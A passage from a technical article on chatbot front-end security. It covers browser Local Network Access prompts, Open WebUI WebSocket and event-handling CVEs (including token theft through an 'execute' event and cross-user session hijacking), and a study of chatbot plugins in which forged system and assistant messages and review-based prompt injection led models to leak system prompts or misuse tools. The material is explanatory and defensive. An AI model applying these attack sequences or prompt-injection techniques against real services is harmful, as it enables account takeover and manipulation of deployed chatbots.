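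Exploit Intel's *CVE-2026-32025* reports that CISA had recorded no exploitation of the flaw. But the limit on guesses failed again in later versions. GCVE's *CVE-2026-41333* (2026) describes a way around it that exposed weak shared passwords in versions before 2026.3.31. OSV's *CVE-2026-62220* (2026) describes another, for non-browser clients, which began with the version that fixed Oasis Security's flaw and lasted until 2026.5.26. Neither bypass would help an attacker guess a long random access token, so a token is safer than a password even on an up-to-date copy.

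### The browser's permission prompt

Other local programs have had similar flaws. *Local Network Access Standard*, a master's thesis at Radboud University (van Ieperen, 2026), describes ASUS driver software that checked only whether the origin contained the text "driverhub.asus.com". An attacker could pass the check with a longer domain name that included this text, and further weaknesses let a website run commands on the computer.

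The thesis also mentions MCP Inspector, a tool for debugging the connections between models and other software. Attackers could reach it by DNS rebinding, in which a hostile site's domain name resolves first to the attacker's server and moments later to an address on the victim's machine. The browser treats both addresses as the same origin, so the same-origin policy does not stop the page from reading the replies. This attack works over plain HTTP, without a WebSocket.

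Browser makers have responded with Local Network Access, a rule that requires a website to get the user's permission before it connects to local programs or devices. The draft specification, WICG's *Local Network Access*, divides addresses into three groups: loopback addresses on the user's own machine, local addresses on the surrounding network, and public addresses on the internet. A page from a public address needs permission to connect to a local or loopback address, and a page from a local address needs permission to connect to a loopback address. So when a script at quiz.example tries to open a socket to localhost, the browser asks the user whether to allow it.

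Chrome introduced the prompt in version 142, but at first it did not cover WebSockets, so neither OpenClaw attack would have triggered it in February 2026. Google's *Chrome 147* (2026) announced that the stable release of 7 April extended the prompt to WebSockets. In Chromium's *Intent to Ship* (2026), the developers said that roughly 0.1% of page loads open such connections, and suspected that fraud-detection scripts inflated this figure.

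Firefox has followed, turning on Local Network Access by default for desktop users in version 153. CyberInsider reports that version 154 also asks for permission when a public website tries to open a WebSocket to the user's machine or local network. MDN's *Firefox 154 release notes for developers* (2026) gives 18 August 2026 as that version's release date.

Safari had no such prompt in August 2026, but it blocks some of these connections for a different reason. Browsers stop encrypted pages from loading most unencrypted content, and Safari applies this rule to localhost, while Chrome and Firefox make an exception. In Safari, a page at https://quiz.example therefore can't open an unencrypted socket to a local program, but the same page at http://quiz.example can, so an attacker only has to serve the page without encryption. In March 2026, a developer reported serving a legitimate site to Safari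 users this way so that it could reach a local program. The report is in Mohanathas's *Don't treat loopback addresses* (2017), a long discussion on the bug tracker for WebKit, Safari's engine.

John Wilander, a WebKit engineer at Apple, wrote in the same discussion in June 2025 that prompts were a "last resort", because ordinary users can't judge whether a website really needs the access. As one alternative, Wilander suggested letting a site connect to a single port of its choice and blocking all the others. This would stop a site from scanning the computer to see which programs are running. It would not protect a gateway on a well-known port such as 18789, because a hostile page could choose that port. Wilander added that browsers could combine the restriction with a prompt.

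WebKit's developers have nevertheless begun to implement Local Network Access. In July 2026, Gower (2026) proposed code for the check in *Add the Local Network Access check algorithm and a NetworkProcess-resident permission stub*. WebKit had no permission prompt yet, so the code would refuse any connection that needed the user's permission.

### After the user clicks Allow

If the user clicks Allow, the hostile page can connect to the gateway much as it could before browsers added the prompt, and only the gateway's Origin check and login can stop it. The specification doesn't fix how much a permission covers, so this can vary by browser. The permission may let a site connect to every program that listens on the machine, and the browser may save the user's choice. Because the permission belongs to the site's origin, an XSS flaw on a site the user has allowed would let an attacker's script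 use that permission.

The browser's permission prompt may not give the user enough information to refuse. The University of Illinois' *Google Chrome Local Network Access Permission* quotes Chrome 142's wording as "Look for and connect to any device on your local network", which doesn't mention an assistant or any other program. MDN's *Local network access* explains that the standard now has separate permissions for the local network and the user's own machine. This helps a user who wants a website to find a printer but not to reach programs on the computer.

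Thomson (2025) reviewed the proposal for the W3C's Technical Architecture Group, which advises on web standards. Thomson argued that consent should be "freely given, specific, and informed" and that the prompt meets none of these conditions, because the site often breaks if the user refuses, the permission is broad, and few people understand the question. Thomson still accepted a prompt as probably the only option against attacks already under way, and some members of the group thought better wording could make the consent meaningful.

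People who run local assistants may be especially likely to click Allow, because some chatbots need the permission to work. One developer in the WebKit discussion offers a browser chat application that connects to Ollama, a program that runs language models on the user's own computer. Van Ieperen crawled 45,000 popular websites and found many local requests, mostly from bot-detection scripts, developers' mistakes and attempts to contact a site's own desktop program. Van Ieperen warns that users may get into the habit of accepting prompts if they often appear for such reasons.

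Chrome also does not show the prompt when a site opens a local page in a full tab or window. In the first OpenClaw attack, the crafted link opened the user's own Control UI, which then connected to a public server. Local Network Access does not restrict connections from a local page to a public server, so it would not have prevented the theft of the access token. Chrome would have asked for permission only at the next step, when the hostile page tried to open a socket to localhost. If the gateway was accessible from the internet, the attacker could skip that step.

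A page served from the user's own machine can connect to localhost without asking for permission. The specification exempts it because software on the device already has the most privileged position on the user's network. But a local page can contain a hostile script, for example if a developer is testing a website that loads a compromised library or if another local tool has an XSS flaw. That script can open a socket to the gateway without a prompt. If the page comes from http://localhost:3000 and the Control UI from http://localhost:18789, their different ports make them different origins, so a gateway that compares the whole Origin header can refuse the connection. A gateway that accepts every localhost origin will let the script try to log in.

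## Does an open socket still check who is using it?

An Origin check and a login restrict who can open a WebSocket, but they don't stop a user from continuing to use it after logging out or changing jobs.

With ordinary HTTP, chat.example receives the cookie or access token again with every request, so it can look up the user each time. Over a WebSocket, it receives this proof only once, when the user connects. If the developers add no further checks, the server may act on outdated answers to three questions for as long as the socket stays open:

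- Is the login still valid?
- Does the user still hold the same role, such as administrator?
- May this user act on this particular conversation, document or session?

The problem is milder when an answer is streamed over SSE. The stream can continue after the user logs out, but it normally ends with the answer, and the next question is a new request that the server can check.

Open WebUI, an open-source chatbot interface that organisations run on their own servers, had all three gaps. It uses Socket.IO to deliver answers, run team channels and shared notes, and execute code in the user's browser. Its maintainers disclosed the flaws below between May and July 2026.

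### Signing out

Open WebUI's access token is a JSON Web Token (JWT), a signed piece of text that contains the user's identifier and an expiry date. The server can verify the signature without looking anything up, but the signature remains valid after the user signs out. To cancel a token before it expires, the server has to keep a record of cancelled tokens and check it.

Open WebUI keeps this record in Redis, a fast data store that several servers can share. *CVE-2026-59219*, an analysis by the security company SecureLayer7, dates the feature to version 0.9.0. When a user signs out, the server records the identifier of a single access token. If a company's central login service reports a logout, the server instead records a revocation time for the user.

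The developers added the lookup only to HTTP requests. According to OSV's *PYSEC-2026-3595*, the code that authenticated connections to Socket.IO and the terminal (a command line that users can open from the chat) checked only the token's signature and expiry date. The person who reported the flaw signed out and reused the old access token. HTTP requests failed with status 401, but Socket.IO still accepted the token.

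This matters most when someone has stolen an access token, because the victim would normally disable it by signing out. After that, the thief could no longer fetch saved conversations over HTTP, but they could still connect as the victim, receive new channel messages and changes to shared notes, and pass the terminal's login if an administrator had set up a terminal server.

Installations without Redis do not count as affected, but only because they are designed not to cancel access tokens when a user signs out. A stolen token keeps working over HTTP as well until it expires, which can take up to four weeks with the default settings, according to Releasebot's *Open WebUI Release Notes* (2026), a copy of the project's notes.

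Version 0.10.0, released on 29 June, fixed the flaw. OSV describes a check that runs when a client connects or joins a channel or note. This stops a thief from opening a new connection, but by itself it does not close one that was already open when the victim signed out. According to the release notes, a signed-out session can also no longer keep a live connection open. Administrators can test this by signing out in one tab and checking whether channel messages still arrive in another.

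SecureLayer7 suggests that anyone unable to upgrade block socket connections at the proxy, the server that passes outside traffic to the application. If the installation lets Socket.IO fall back to repeated HTTP requests, the proxy has to block those too.

### Losing a role

When a user connected to Open WebUI, the server copied their account record, including their role, into a table in memory called the session pool. The browser then sent regular "heartbeat" messages to show that it was still connected. Each heartbeat updated the time of last contact but left the role unchanged.

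CVELogic's *Stale Admin Role in Socket.IO Session Pool*, a copy of the project's advisory, describes what happened when one administrator demoted another. The database was updated at once, and HTTP requests used the new role because each one looked up the account there. But the code for shared notes took the role from the session pool, which still held the old one. A demoted administrator who kept the browser open could still read and overwrite any user's notes. Deleting the account did not remove this access either, because the socket stayed open with the old role.

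Even without the flaw, a dishonest administrator could have copied the notes before losing the role. The flaw also let them read and change whatever people wrote afterwards, while the administrator who had demoted them believed their access had ended.

The maintainers fixed this flaw in version 0.9.0, but similar gaps remained. Until version 0.11.0, in July, an account that had lost both the user and the administrator role could keep its channels and shared notes open. Since version 0.11.1, in August, every role change ends the person's live sessions, including changes that come from a company directory or a login service. The browser then reconnects automatically and receives the new role.

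### Using someone else's session

A user with a valid login and the right role may still specify an object that belongs to someone else. In CVE-2026-59216, that object was another person's browser session.

Open WebUI's built-in interpreter can run a model's Python code in the user's browser. The server sends the code over the user's socket in an "execute:python" event, and the page runs it. A user may have several tabs open, so the front end includes a session number that identifies its socket in the HTTP request that carries the question.

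The server took the session number from the request and checked only that somebody was connected under it. Anyone who knew another user's session number could make the server send code to that user's browser. A user with read access to a shared note could join it and receive the live session numbers of everyone who had it open.

OSV's *PYSEC-2026-3592* (2026) describes how an attacker with an ordinary account could combine the two faults:

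1. The attacker shares a note with an administrator.
2. The administrator opens it, and the attacker learns the administrator's session number from the note.
3. The attacker sends a chat request from their own account but puts the administrator's session number in it. They select a model they control, so that it returns exactly the code they want.
4. The server finds the session number in its pool and sends the code to the administrator's browser.
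5. The code runs in the administrator's page, and the server accepts its requests as the administrator's own.

The attacker gains control of the victim's account. If the victim is an administrator, the attacker can also run programs on the server. Administrators can install "functions", which are Python programs that the server executes, and the attacker's code can install one from the administrator's browser. In the default container, the packaged environment in which Open WebUI runs, the function has root rights, the highest level of access.

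The reporter confirmed the whole sequence on version 0.9.6. It worked only if the code interpreter was on and the administrator was online with the note open. The fault was that another user could act through an administrator's session. Functions worked as intended, since administrators are meant to be able to run code on the server.

The chat request arrived over plain HTTP with a valid login, so the server could identify the sender. It stored the sender's user identifier beside the session number but never compared the sender with the session's owner. The fix in version 0.10.0 adds that comparison. SecureLayer7's *CVE-2026-59216* notes that the attacker cannot forge the user identifier, because the server derives it from the login rather than from the request.

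A flaw in Open WebUI's terminal also let a caller impersonate another user. The server opened a second WebSocket to the terminal program and put a session identifier and the user's identifier in that connection's address. According to Bitsight's *CVE-2026-59224 Details*, the server did not encode the session identifier, so a caller could insert extra text that made the terminal program treat them as a different user. Version 0.10.0 fixed this as well.

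### Events that skipped a check

Shared notes had two simpler faults. OSV's *CVE-2026-44564* describes how a user with read-only access could edit a note. A user needed only read permission to join the note's room, which is the group of connections that receive its updates. When an edit arrived, the server checked that the sender was in the room but not that they had write permission. It then passed the edit to everyone else who had the note open.

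In CVE-2026-59715, the sender did not need an account. Open WebUI accepted every Socket.IO connection, even without an access token, and relied on each event handler, the function that processes one kind of event, to check for a login. OSV's *PYSEC-2026-3599* (2026) lists three note handlers that checked correctly and two that did not. One announced a participant's cursor position, and the other announced that a participant had left.

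A stranger who knew a note's identifier could use these handlers to show fake cursors under any user's name or make it seem that people had left, but could not read or change the note's text. The researcher found the flaw by reviewing the source code with help from Claude, Anthropic's model, and confirmed it on a running copy of version 0.8.12.

A server that expects an access token in the first message has to accept the connection before login, so doing this is not in itself a mistake. But every handler must then check that the connection is authenticated, and a developer who adds a new handler can easily forget the check. Refusing all events from unauthenticated connections in one place, before any handler runs, removes that risk.

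### How serious were they?

| Flaw | What the server failed to check | Affected versions | Fixed in | Severity out of 10 |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| CVE-2026-59219 | Whether the user had signed out | 0.9.0 to 0.9.6, with Redis | 0.10.0 | 7.1 |
| CVE-2026-44553 | Whether the user was still an administrator | Up to 0.8.12 | 0.9.0 | 8.1 |
| CVE-2026-59216 | Whether the session belonged to the requester | Up to 0.9.6 | 0.10.0 | 7.7 or 9.0 |
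| CVE-2026-44564 | Whether a reader could also write | Before 0.9.0 | 0.9.0 | 5.4 |
| CVE-2026-59715 | Whether the sender had logged in | 0.6.16 to 0.9.6 | 0.10.0 | 3.1 or 6.5 |

exploitDog's *CVE-2026-59216* (2026), an entry in a Russian vulnerability catalogue, lists both scores for the flaw. Halo Security's *Open WebUI Remote Code Execution Vulnerability* uses the higher one and calls the flaw critical. The advisory's 7.7 assumes a difficult attack that needs some action by the victim, which is fair because the victim has to open a note. It also assumes no effect on the server's availability. That fits an attack on an ordinary user, but an attacker with root rights could shut the service down. The higher score seems more realistic where administrators use their powerful accounts for everyday chats and notes.

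The advisory for CVE-2026-59715 gives it a score of 3.1 on the assumption that the attacker has an account, although the flaw is that no account is needed. The US National Vulnerability Database (NVD) corrects this in its score of 6.5, which the security company Intruder repeats. The NVD also adds some loss of availability, because a stranger could open any number of connections. It rates the attack as easy, which is right for flooding the server with connections but understates the difficulty of creating fake cursors. For those, the attacker needs a note's identifier, which is practically impossible to guess if the server generates it at random. Under the same scoring formula, a difficult attack that needs no login and has the effects listed by the NVD would score 4.8.

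The advisory scores the demoted-administrator flaw at 8.1, and Enginsight's *CVE-2026-44553* lists the same score from NIST, the US standards agency. That is higher than the advisory's score for an attack that can end with control of the server. The 8.1 score is based on the attacker being an ordinary user, which they are by the time they misuse the socket, but they must have opened it as an administrator. Counting that as a requirement would lower the score to 6.5.

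### Repairing the checks

HTTP requests were already safe in the sign-out and demotion cases, so the developers had written the right checks but not applied them to the socket. The most reliable repair is to have both call the same function. At chat.example, it might work like this:

```
authorize(access_token, action, object):
    if the access token has expired or been revoked:
        refuse, and close the socket if there is one
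    user = read the account from the database
    if the account is missing or deactivated:
        refuse, and close the socket if there is one
    if this user may not do this action to this object:
        refuse this request or event
```

An HTTP handler calls the function for each request, and a socket handler calls it for each event, using the access token that the server stored when the user connected. Any rule the developers later add to the function applies to both. Open WebUI's fix for signed-out access tokens handles revocation this way, with one helper function for HTTP, Socket.IO and the terminal.

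Reading the account for every event takes time, and a shared-notes editor can send several events per second for each person typing. Open WebUI stopped re-reading the account for typing indicators and shared-document edits in version 0.11.0, apparently for this reason. A server can safely keep a copy of the role in memory if every route that changes a role also updates the copy or closes the socket, but developers can easily miss a route, as the later fixes for role changes show. A cautious compromise is to read the account again for any event that exposes or changes data, and to use the copy only for trivial events such as cursor movements.

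Checks on incoming events also miss a user who only listens. Once a socket has joined a channel's room, the server sends it every new message without waiting for a request. If the user then loses access to the channel, the server has to close the socket or remove it from the room, because there is no incoming event to check.

To close sockets on logout, the server has to keep a list of which sockets belong to which login. If chat.example runs on several servers, the one that handles the logout also has to notify the others, because the user's second tab may be connected to one of them. A password change should close the sockets of every device that logged in with the old password. Open WebUI started ending the logins on those devices in version 0.11.1, but only on installations with Redis. The server can also set a timer that closes each socket when its access token expires, and require a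 new handshake every hour or so in case another mechanism fails.

Session numbers need a different fix, because knowing a session number does not prove that someone owns the session. The server should take the user's identity from the login and then check that the session belongs to that user. OSV also recommends hiding other participants' numbers as an extra precaution, though the ownership check works even if everyone knows them. The front end could still tell the cursors apart if each participant had a random label that means nothing outside that note.

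The same applies to a user's name or identifier inside an event. The faulty cursor handler accepted any user identifier the sender supplied. Wiz's *CVE-2026-59715* reports that the repaired version instead uses the identity from the login and checks that the sender has joined the note.

### Limiting what a connection can use

Even a properly authenticated user can overload a server. Many websites limit how many HTTP requests a visitor may make per minute, but opening a WebSocket counts as only one request, however many messages follow. The application therefore has to count the messages itself, and it should count them per account because a user can get around a per-socket limit by opening more sockets. Setting different limits for different events also helps, since a question to the model uses far more resources than a typing indicator.

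A server can't limit connections per account before users log in, so it has to cap unauthenticated connections per network address. According to the advisory, the versions of Open WebUI affected by CVE-2026-59715 had no such cap.

Message size matters because some processing slows disproportionately as text gets longer. NixOS, a Linux distribution that tracks flaws in the software it packages, lists one such flaw in Open WebUI, with a severity of 6.5. The server searched each chat message for references to "skills", which are saved instructions for the model. If a reference started but never ended, the search time grew with the square of the message's length, so a message ten times as long could take a hundred times as long. The search also blocked the loop that serves all users, so one logged-in person could freeze the whole installation. The flaw affected versions 0.9.2 to 0.9.6 and did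 not depend on WebSockets. A size limit would have bounded the delay, but the proper remedy was a better search pattern.

Limits that are too strict also cause failures. Until version 0.11.1, Open WebUI could cut off an answer when the model provider sent an unusually large piece, such as a long passage of reasoning. The server should set a limit for each message type that is high enough for legitimate messages, perhaps a few hundred characters for a cursor position and far more for a document.

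The server can also send more data than it needs to. Before the same version, Open WebUI sent the whole answer so far again with every update. For an answer in 2,000 equal pieces, it sent 1 + 2 + 3 + … + 2,000 pieces, or about two million. Sending only the new text takes 2,000 pieces, about a thousandth as many, which matches the developers' statement that the change cut the data by up to 1,000 times for a very long reply. Under the old method, a user could cause a great deal of traffic with one short question that asked for a long answer.

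### When the browser leaves

After a user closes a chatbot's page, the model can keep generating the answer and the server can keep receiving it from the model provider. Users sometimes want this, for example when a phone briefly loses its signal. Since version 0.11.1, Open WebUI has kept unfinished replies on the server in installations with Redis, so a user who refreshes the page can rejoin the answer in progress.

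Because chat.example keeps generating an answer after the browser disconnects, an attacker can send a question that takes a lot of computation to answer, disconnect and repeat. The attacker never holds more than one socket open, so a cap on connections does not stop them. chat.example also needs to limit how many answers each account can have in progress, whether or not a browser is connected, and how long each answer can run.

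A stop button does not always stop the work either. Releasebot's notes for Open WebUI list two such faults as ordinary bugs rather than vulnerabilities. Before version 0.11.2, a stopped answer could run to its end on installations that spread users across several servers with a Redis cluster. A later release fixed a separate fault on installations without shared Redis state, where a stopped reply could keep calling tools until it reached its own limit.

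Version 0.13.0, released on 3 November 2026, raised that limit from 256 to 1,024 rounds of tool calls per response. At ten seconds per round, a reply that nobody is watching could run for nearly three hours, compared with 43 minutes before. The release also removed the default limits on sub-agents, the background helpers a model can delegate work to. Administrators can set stricter limits on both, and should if they open the service to people they don't know.

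Stopping an answer also requires permission. Before version 0.11.0, a user who knew the ID of someone else's chat could interrupt its answer by trying to delete the chat. The server refused the deletion, but only after cancelling the answer.

Tasks that run without an open browser can continue after the user loses permission to request them. Open WebUI's scheduled automations, which send prompts at set times, used to keep running after an administrator deactivated the owner's account. Since version 0.10.0, the server has checked the owner's account and permissions before each run. The server needs to make a similar check before each tool call in a long reply, because the user may have lost access to the tool since asking the question.

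## Which messages do the browser and the server accept without checking?

Even if chat.example has verified who sent a message, it still has to check what that message is allowed to do. A chat stream carries more than the answer's text, and each message usually has a field that determines how the receiver handles the rest of the message. If the receiver always follows this field, a stranger may be able to do things that the developers meant only for themselves.

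From server to browser, the field is usually a type. In OpenAI's streaming format, one piece of an answer can contain text, audio or a function call, which is the model's request to run a tool. Open WebUI adds its own types. In September 2025, Open WebUI's *Events*, part of the project's documentation, listed a dozen kinds of event, including these:

| Type | What the page does | What a hostile sender could do with it |
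|---|---|---|
| message | Adds text to the answer | Give a false answer |
| replace | Replaces the whole answer | Change an answer the user has already read |
| source | Adds a citation | Credit a false claim to a real document |
| input | Opens a box and returns what the user types | Ask for a password |
| execute | Runs JavaScript contained in the event | Do almost anything the user can do |

An "input" message contains no code, but a hostile sender could use one to ask the user for a password, as the documentation's example does.

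The role field in messages sent from the browser to the server can matter just as much. A language model receives a conversation as a list of messages, each labeled with a role. A "system" message contains the developer's instructions, a "user" message contains the visitor's words, an "assistant" message contains the model's earlier answers, and a "tool" message contains a tool's output. Model makers train their models to give system messages priority over user messages, so whoever sets the role influences how much priority the model gives the text.

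### An event that ran code

Open WebUI has a feature called Direct Connections, which lets users connect to any model server that follows OpenAI's format. Simonovich (2026), in *Vulnerability Discovered in Open WebUI Enables Account Takeover and Remote Code Execution*, describes how such a server could run a script in the user's page. Simonovich, who works for the security company Cato Networks, reported the flaw in October 2025, and it became CVE-2025-64496. The attack had three preconditions:

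- An administrator had turned on Direct Connections, which is off by default.
- A user had added the attacker's server, perhaps because someone recommended it as a free alternative to GPT-4.
- The user sent a message to the model on that server. Any message would do.

OSV's *GHSA-cm35-v4vp-5xvx* (2025), a copy of the project's advisory, gives the rest of the sequence:

1. The attacker's server starts streaming a reply and includes an event of the type "execute", with JavaScript inside it.
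2. The front end passes the JavaScript to new Function(), a browser feature that turns text into a program, and runs it.
3. The script reads the user's access token from localStorage, a store that any script from the page's origin can read.
4. The script sends the access token to the attacker.

In the test, this took about five seconds. The stolen access token had no expiry date, and in these versions signing out did not cancel it.

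The attacker could now read the victim's conversations and files. They could also run programs on the server if the victim had the right permissions. Simonovich describes a victim with the "workspace.tools" permission, which lets users create tools whose Python code the server runs without a sandbox. OSV describes the theft of an administrator's access token, which lets the attacker install a function instead. If the victim could neither create tools nor install functions, the attacker gained access only to the victim's account.

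Simonovich recommends keeping the login in a short-lived HttpOnly cookie, although the script could still have created a tool from the victim's own page. Simonovich also recommends a strict Content Security Policy, a list sent by the server of the places a page may load scripts and other content from. A strict policy also blocks new Function(), so it would have stopped the attack, but it would also have blocked Open WebUI's legitimate uses of "execute".

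### The fix in version 0.6.35

The maintainers' first patch, on 19 October, was incomplete. They completed the fix in version 0.6.35 on 6 November. According to the release notes, reproduced in alexlebens.dev's *Update ghcr.io/open-webui/open-webui Docker tag to v0.6.35* (2025), Open WebUI now blocks every event from a directly connected model server, not just "execute".

The security company Miggo located the change in the server code that forwards the stream to the page, and had no front-end patch to analyse. The front end still has its "execute" handler. According to a March 2026 edition of Open WebUI's *Events*, the handler runs code with full access to the page, and developers should use it only in trusted functions. Keeping the handler is defensible, since an administrator who installs a function already trusts its author with the server. But the page will run any code the server passes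 on, so Open WebUI's developers have to block untrusted senders on every route through the server. The later flaw that let Python code reach another user's browser involved a different route.

The advisory describes CVE-2025-64496 as an SSE flaw because the attacker's server streamed its reply over SSE. A WebSocket would have delivered the same event to the same handler, and an Origin check would not have stopped it because the user had chosen to connect to the attacker's server.

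The event probably travelled part of the way over a WebSocket. According to the March 2026 documentation, Open WebUI's server sends streamed answers to the page over Socket.IO, and the maintainers put the fix in the server's forwarding code. Version 0.6.35 also added an Origin check for WebSocket connections, but that check was meant to prevent cross-site hijacking.

### Conflicting versions and scores

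The sources differ on which versions had the flaw. OSV lists 0.6.33, the version on which the finder tested the attack, and below. Simonovich gives 0.6.34 and older. GitLab's *CVE-2025-64496* (2025) repeats OSV's figure in its description but lists every version before 0.6.35 as affected. NVD's *CVE-2025-64496 Detail* gives "0.6.224 and prior", which is probably a typing error, because 0.6.224 would come after the version NVD lists as fixed. Only Snyk's *Inclusion of Web Functionality from an Untrusted Source Affecting open-webui package* (2025) adds a lower limit, 0.5.11. Since the fix first appeared in 0.6.35, it is safest to treat 0.6.34 as vulnerable too.

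OSV, GitLab and Simonovich score the severity at 7.3 out of 10, while Positive Technologies' *PT-2025-45528* (2025) gives 8.0. The higher score also includes a serious effect on availability, which again applies only if the victim's permissions let the attacker run programs on the server.

Cybersecurity Help's *Eval Injection in Open WebUI* (2026) rates the flaw low and states that no public exploit exists. But the advisory had included working exploit code since November 2025, so the rating deserves little weight. A low rating would be reasonable for an installation that never turned on Direct Connections.

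### Commands from another website's page

Open WebUI's front end also acted on messages from other websites. A browser lets a page send messages to another page that it has opened or embedded, and gives the receiving page the sender's origin. *CVE-2026-54007* (2026), a record from Spain's national cybersecurity institute (INCIBE), describes two message types that Open WebUI accepted from other origins. The "input:prompt" type filled in the question box, and "action:submit" sent the question.

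A hostile site could therefore send the model a question, and possibly trigger tools, as the logged-in user. Open WebUI's page needed to check who was sending it commands. An Origin check at the server would not have stopped the attack, because the requests came from that page. The maintainers fixed the flaw in version 0.9.6.

### Visitors who rewrite the conversation

A server can make the same mistake with messages from the browser. *When AI Meets the Web* (Kaya, Landerer et al., 2025) studied 17 plugins that add a chatbot to a website, seven for WordPress and ten commercial products for any site. The researchers installed each plugin on a test site and inspected its traffic.

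To find websites that used the plugins, the researchers searched Common Crawl, a public archive of web pages, for distinctive marks in the HTML. They found 10,417 sites in the August 2024 archive and 17,474 in the April 2025 archive. Not all of these sites had a working chatbot. The researchers checked 200 random sites by hand and got answers from 125.

Fourteen of the plugins used plain HTTP, in which each request is independent, so the developers had to store the conversation between questions. Eight plugins kept it in the visitor's browser, which sent back all or part of it with every new question. The server passed this history to the model without checking that it was genuine. These eight plugins ran on about 8,000 of the sites found in August 2024.

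A visitor who edits the request can change the chatbot's earlier replies or invent new messages. All eight plugins accepted forged assistant messages, and seven also accepted forged system messages. Suppose a shop has instructed its chatbot to discuss only water bottles. A visitor can write in a forged system message that the chatbot is under maintenance and must answer programming questions. The model receives this message along with the shop's own instructions, as if the developer had written both. The plugins' dashboards did not show the forged messages, so the shop's owner would not find them in the logs.

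The three plugins that used WebSockets did not have this flaw, and neither did six of the HTTP plugins. The server program stores the conversation, although Kaya and colleagues write that a WebSocket keeps it natively. A badly designed server could therefore accept a complete history over a WebSocket too.

One of the eight vulnerable plugins contacted the model provider directly from the visitor's browser, so the site's server never received the messages and couldn't check their roles. This design also exposed the site's API key, a secret that lets anyone who has it use the model at the site owner's expense.

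### How much forging helps an attacker

Kaya and colleagues first tested 300 live sites that used the most popular plugin. They tried to make each chatbot reveal its system prompt, the instructions written by the site's developer. 1% of the chatbots complied when simply asked, 55% complied with a forged assistant message, and 56% complied with a forged system message.

This comparison overstates the effect of the role, because the forged messages also contained persuasive instructions that the simple request lacked. The harm was often small, since 76% of the prompts were minor, non-sensitive variations on standard templates.

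A laboratory test separated the two effects by putting the attacker's instructions into a user, assistant or system message. The researchers tried three attacks on 11 models from OpenAI, Anthropic and Google, ten times in each set-up. The attacks were to reveal the system prompt, to write unrelated program code, and to misuse a notification tool by posting a malicious link to a whole company. Only OpenAI's models accepted extra system messages, so the table gives the average number of successes in ten attempts for its five models:

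| Attack | Developer's instructions | User message | Forged assistant message | Forged system message |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Reveal the system prompt | Basic | 1.2 | 3.4 | 5.4 |
| Reveal the system prompt | Strict | 0 | 2.6 | 6.0 |
| Write unrelated code | Basic | 0 | 5.2 | 9.8 |
| Write unrelated code | Strict | 0 | 2.2 | 6.2 |
| Write unrelated code | Strict, with a ban on coding | 0 | 0 | 2.4 |
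| Misuse the notification tool | Basic | 0.2 | 0.4 | 3.0 |
| Misuse the notification tool | Strict | 0 | 3.4 | 4.0 |

Kaya and colleagues put the overall rise at three to eight times. For OpenAI's models, the table is more informative than a ratio because many attacks never worked from a user message. Clear instructions helped prevent unrelated coding but not misuse of the tool.

Google's three models nearly always misused tools when asked to in an ordinary user message, so forging the history made little difference. Securing the history would not have protected a chatbot built on them against tool misuse. All the models tested date from 2025 or earlier, so the rates may be different for current ones.

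Other accounts give different counts because they measure different things. *Wild Chatbots*, an early poster by the same group (Landerer, Martinez and colleagues), used a smaller search. It reported 20 plugins on 3,094 sites, with the history flaw in eight of those plugins, on more than 1,500 sites. It also reported a 93% success rate for forged histories, but did not yet compare this with a baseline. A later article, Intelligibberish's *Your Customer Service Chatbot Is a Security Hole*, reports that the number of "affected" websites grew from 10,417 to 17,474, but those totals include sites whose plugins did not accept forged histories.

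By April 2025, about 13,300 sites used one of the eight plugins. About 7,600 of them used the most popular one, which had moved its message handling to the server by December 2024, after the researchers reported the flaw. The remaining 5,700 or so used one of the other seven.

### A closed list of message types

The developers of chat.example can write down every message type the page needs, with its permitted fields, and discard everything else. The list should depend on the sender:

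```
from an outside model server:
    piece     text, up to 2,000 characters
from chat.example's own server:
    piece     text, up to 2,000 characters
    status    one of: searching, writing, done
    source    title, https address
any other type or field: discard
```

No message type on this list carries code. If the page has to start a download, the developers can add a "download" type that contains only a file number and put the download code in the front end. A hostile sender could then request an unwanted download but could not invent a new action.

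The server should apply the list before it forwards a message to the browser, because it can identify where the message came from. The front end should check the type and fields again, in case the developers missed a route through the server. For messages from the browser to the server, only the server's check can be relied on, because a visitor can bypass the front end.

Unknown fields need the same treatment as unknown types. CraftedSignal (2026) describes a flaw in Open WebUI up to version 0.6.43 in which a user could add an "embeds" field to the saved chat history, and its content later ran as script. The list can't catch a script inside the text of an ordinary "piece", so the page has to handle such scripts when it displays the answer.

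### Keeping or signing the history

The simplest repair for forged histories is to store the conversation on the server. The browser then sends only a conversation number and the new question:

```
on question(chat, text):
    refuse unless this user owns the chat
    history = load the saved messages of this chat
    add text to history with the role "user"
    send the developer's instructions and history to the model
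```

The second most popular plugin still accepted forged messages after the researchers' report, although it now logs a warning. Its developers explained that some features rely on changing earlier messages. A server can support many such features without trusting the whole history. For example, it can let a visitor edit one of their own questions, then delete everything after it and generate a new answer.

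If the developers want the browser to hold the conversation, the server can sign it. Kaya and colleagues suggest signing each genuine message with a secret known only to the server. But if the signature covers only that message, a visitor can still leave out a refusal or copy a genuine answer from another conversation. It is safer to sign everything together:

```
signature = HMAC(secret key, chat number + all messages with their roles)
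```

HMAC is a function that computes a short code from a text and a key. If the visitor changes a single character, the code no longer matches, and they can't compute a new one without the key. A visitor can still send back an older copy of the conversation with its valid code. This is usually harmless, but if the chatbot has since issued a refund, the older copy would omit it. A chatbot that can take such actions should keep its records on the server.

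### Assigning roles on the server

The server should never accept a message's role from the browser. It should label new text from a visitor as a user message and reserve the system role for the developer's instructions.

The server must also label text from other sources correctly. Fifteen of the 17 plugins could collect text from the website, including customers' reviews and comments, to help the chatbot answer questions. Seven of them gave this text to the model as a system message. A customer could therefore write instructions in a review, and the plugin would present them to the model as the developer's.

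To see whether chatbots received such text, Kaya and colleagues checked 100 online shops that used the most popular plugin. In 13 of them, the chatbot repeated details from customers' reviews. The researchers did not plant any instructions on these sites. In their laboratory tests, text from a web page was least likely to mislead the model if it arrived as a tool message. Even then, and with strict instructions, about 5 to 10% of attacks succeeded, so the server also has to check any action the model requests after reading the text.

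## When does a model's text become code in the page?

An ordinary piece of an answer passes chat.example's list of permitted message types, but it becomes dangerous if the front end turns part of its text into a script. This can happen with any transport, at several steps between the model's Markdown and the finished page.

Suppose the model at chat.example has finished this answer:

```
Water boils at about **90 °C** at 3,000 metres.
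See the [altitude table](https://chat.example/altitude).
```

A Markdown parser turns it into HTML:

```
<p>Water boils at about <strong>90 °C</strong> at 3,000 metres.
See the <a href="https://chat.example/altitude">altitude table</a>.</p>
```

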